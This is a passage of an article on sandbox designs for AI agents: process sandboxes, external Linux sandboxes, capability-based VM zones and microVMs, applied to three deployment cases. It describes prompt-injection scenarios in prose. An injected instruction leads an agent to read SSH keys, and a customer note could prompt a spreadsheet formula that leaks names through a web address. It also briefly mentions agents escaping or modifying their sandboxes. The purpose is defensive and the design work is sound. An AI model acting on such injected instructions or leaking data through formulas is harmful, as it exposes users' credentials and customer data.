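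In September 2026, TNG Technology Consulting's *AI Insight #5* compared four sandboxes against six kinds of attack. The sandboxes were Claude Code's own, nono, and two that TNG built, one based on Docker containers. None blocked every attack, although TNG considers any of them better than no sandbox. The test included no virtual machine as such, so it can't show whether one would have done better.

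### Willison's external sandboxes

A host can run code in a virtual machine and still control what each command may access. *External sandboxes for coding agents* (Willison, 2026) describes three prototypes of this design, which Willison released in November with Prime Radiant, an AI research lab. The agent runs on the user's Mac, and all its commands run on a separate Linux system.

Suppose the clerk's agent needs to total `orders.csv` with `awk`. It sends the command to a sandbox server on the same computer. The server runs it in a Linux system that contains only the folders the clerk has mounted, each either read-only or writable. The command prints 4000, and the server returns this to the agent. If the agent follows an injected instruction to read the clerk's SSH keys, the command fails because those files don't exist in the Linux system.

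By default, commands have no network access. The clerk can turn on a proxy that allows access to particular hosts and adds credentials outside the sandbox. A web page shows the requests commands have made and lets the clerk change the rules while the sandbox runs.

All three prototypes accept the same requests, so users can switch between them without changing agents. One uses Apple's container software and another uses QEMU, a general virtual machine program. The third runs v86, a simulated processor written for WebAssembly. It needs only Node.js, a common program for running JavaScript, so it is the easiest to try, but simulating a processor in software is slow. An earlier v86 tool that Willison made for web browsers took 10 to 30 seconds to start. The v86 prototype also relies on the WebAssembly runtime for protection instead of the processor's hardware separation.

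The design covers only what the agent sends to the sandbox. Willison's instructions for the coding agent Pi therefore turn off its built-in tools, which would otherwise read and edit files directly on the Mac. A mail tool the clerk connected to the agent would also run outside the sandbox.

Willison decided against putting the agent in the sandbox because the agent might then modify itself or its surroundings. Keeping it outside also makes the boundary easier to check. Anthropic moved Cowork's agent out of its virtual machine because the product became unusable whenever the machine failed to start. The original arrangement had the advantage that nothing outside the machine could allow a command to run without protection. A host that keeps the agent outside should therefore refuse commands when the sandbox is unavailable rather than run them directly on the user's computer.

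### Edera's capabilities and separate machines

Edera combines virtual machines with object capabilities. Each agent runs in a "zone", a virtual machine with its own kernel. Edera's *Bounded Authority for AI Agents* describes narrow capabilities that let the agent take a particular action without holding the credential that action requires.

In the company's example, an agent needs to change one project on GitHub. Normally, it would hold a GitHub token and rely on a separate policy to decide what the token may do. The agent might then be able to reach every project that the token covers. Edera instead aims to give it something closer to this:

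`capability = write(project-a)`

The capability identifies the project and permits the change, as Hardy's capabilities did for the compiler's files. Someone who takes over the agent can still damage that project, but they don't get a token that works elsewhere.

Edera also proposes splitting a task among agents in separate zones, each with only the data that another agent passes to it. For the orders task, one agent could have a capability to read pending orders, and a second could have a capability to email the manager. If hostile code took over the second agent's kernel, it would have the $4,000 total and could email the manager, but it could not access the database.

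This design deals with both arguments as long as the software behind the capabilities runs outside the zone and checks each request. The zones also shouldn't share a package store or other service where agents can leave each other instructions.

### Three cases

Suppose a clerk keeps orders in a spreadsheet and wants an assistant to add up columns and highlight large amounts. The assistant needs to read and write cells, but it doesn't need a shell or ordinary Linux programs. A small interpreter suits this well. The host can supply one function that reads cells in the open sheet and another that writes them, and the program starts almost instantly.

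The most likely attack is an instruction in a customer's note, and the interpreter gives the assistant no direct way to act on it outside the sheet. The assistant could still send data out indirectly, because some spreadsheet programs have formulas that load data from a web address. If it wrote such a formula with a customer's name in the address, the spreadsheet would send the name when it loaded the page. The host's write function should therefore accept only plain values and formulas on an approved list.

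A virtual machine would add little here as long as the interpreter handles one person's data. Running the interpreter in a restricted process would still make sense, given how quickly people escaped from Monty. If the assistant later needs Python's charting packages, the company could run that code in a microVM with no network access and send it only the columns for the chart.

A coding agent on a laptop needs compilers, package managers and tests, which rules out a small interpreter. A process sandbox is a reasonable choice when the project is familiar and the developer is watching. Anthropic says adding one to Claude Code cut permission prompts by 84%. But the default settings leave cloud credentials readable, so the developer should block those files. The developer should also approve only the network hosts the project needs and restrict the agent's other tools separately.

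A microVM is the better choice if the agent will work unattended or run code from an unfamiliar project. It takes a fraction of a second to start, and the developer can mount the project folder without the rest of the home directory. Credentials should stay outside the microVM and have narrow permissions.

Neither a lightweight layer nor a virtual machine protects the project itself. Prasakis accepts that an agent in SideKernel can read, change or destroy anything in the mounted folder. The agent could also add a script that the developer later runs outside the sandbox. A developer writing on Docker's site had stopped reviewing individual changes and wouldn't have noticed if an agent had altered a Git script. Developers should keep a separate copy of the project, review any scripts the agent has changed, and run the project's code inside the sandbox until they have done that review.

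A service that runs strangers' code should give each customer a separate microVM, because some customers may deliberately attack the service or one another, and a single kernel flaw could expose everyone on the same server. A thousand Firecracker microVMs would add about 5 GiB of memory overhead, on top of what their own operating systems and programs use. The service should also put a system-call filter around each microVM and install hypervisor updates promptly.

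Some large services don't use a separate virtual machine for each customer. Cloudflare uses isolates, and according to Pillar Security, the sandbox provider Modal runs more than 20,000 containers with gVisor. Anthropic also uses gVisor when Claude runs code on the company's servers. These companies can afford staff to maintain the extra defences. A small company without a security team would do better to rent microVMs from a provider that keeps them updated.

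The service also has to control who can start code and what that code can contact. During the July incident, OpenAI's model could run code in sandboxes belonging to one of Modal's customers because the customer's service was open to anyone on the internet, with no login. Modal's technology chief said that nobody had broken the company's isolation.
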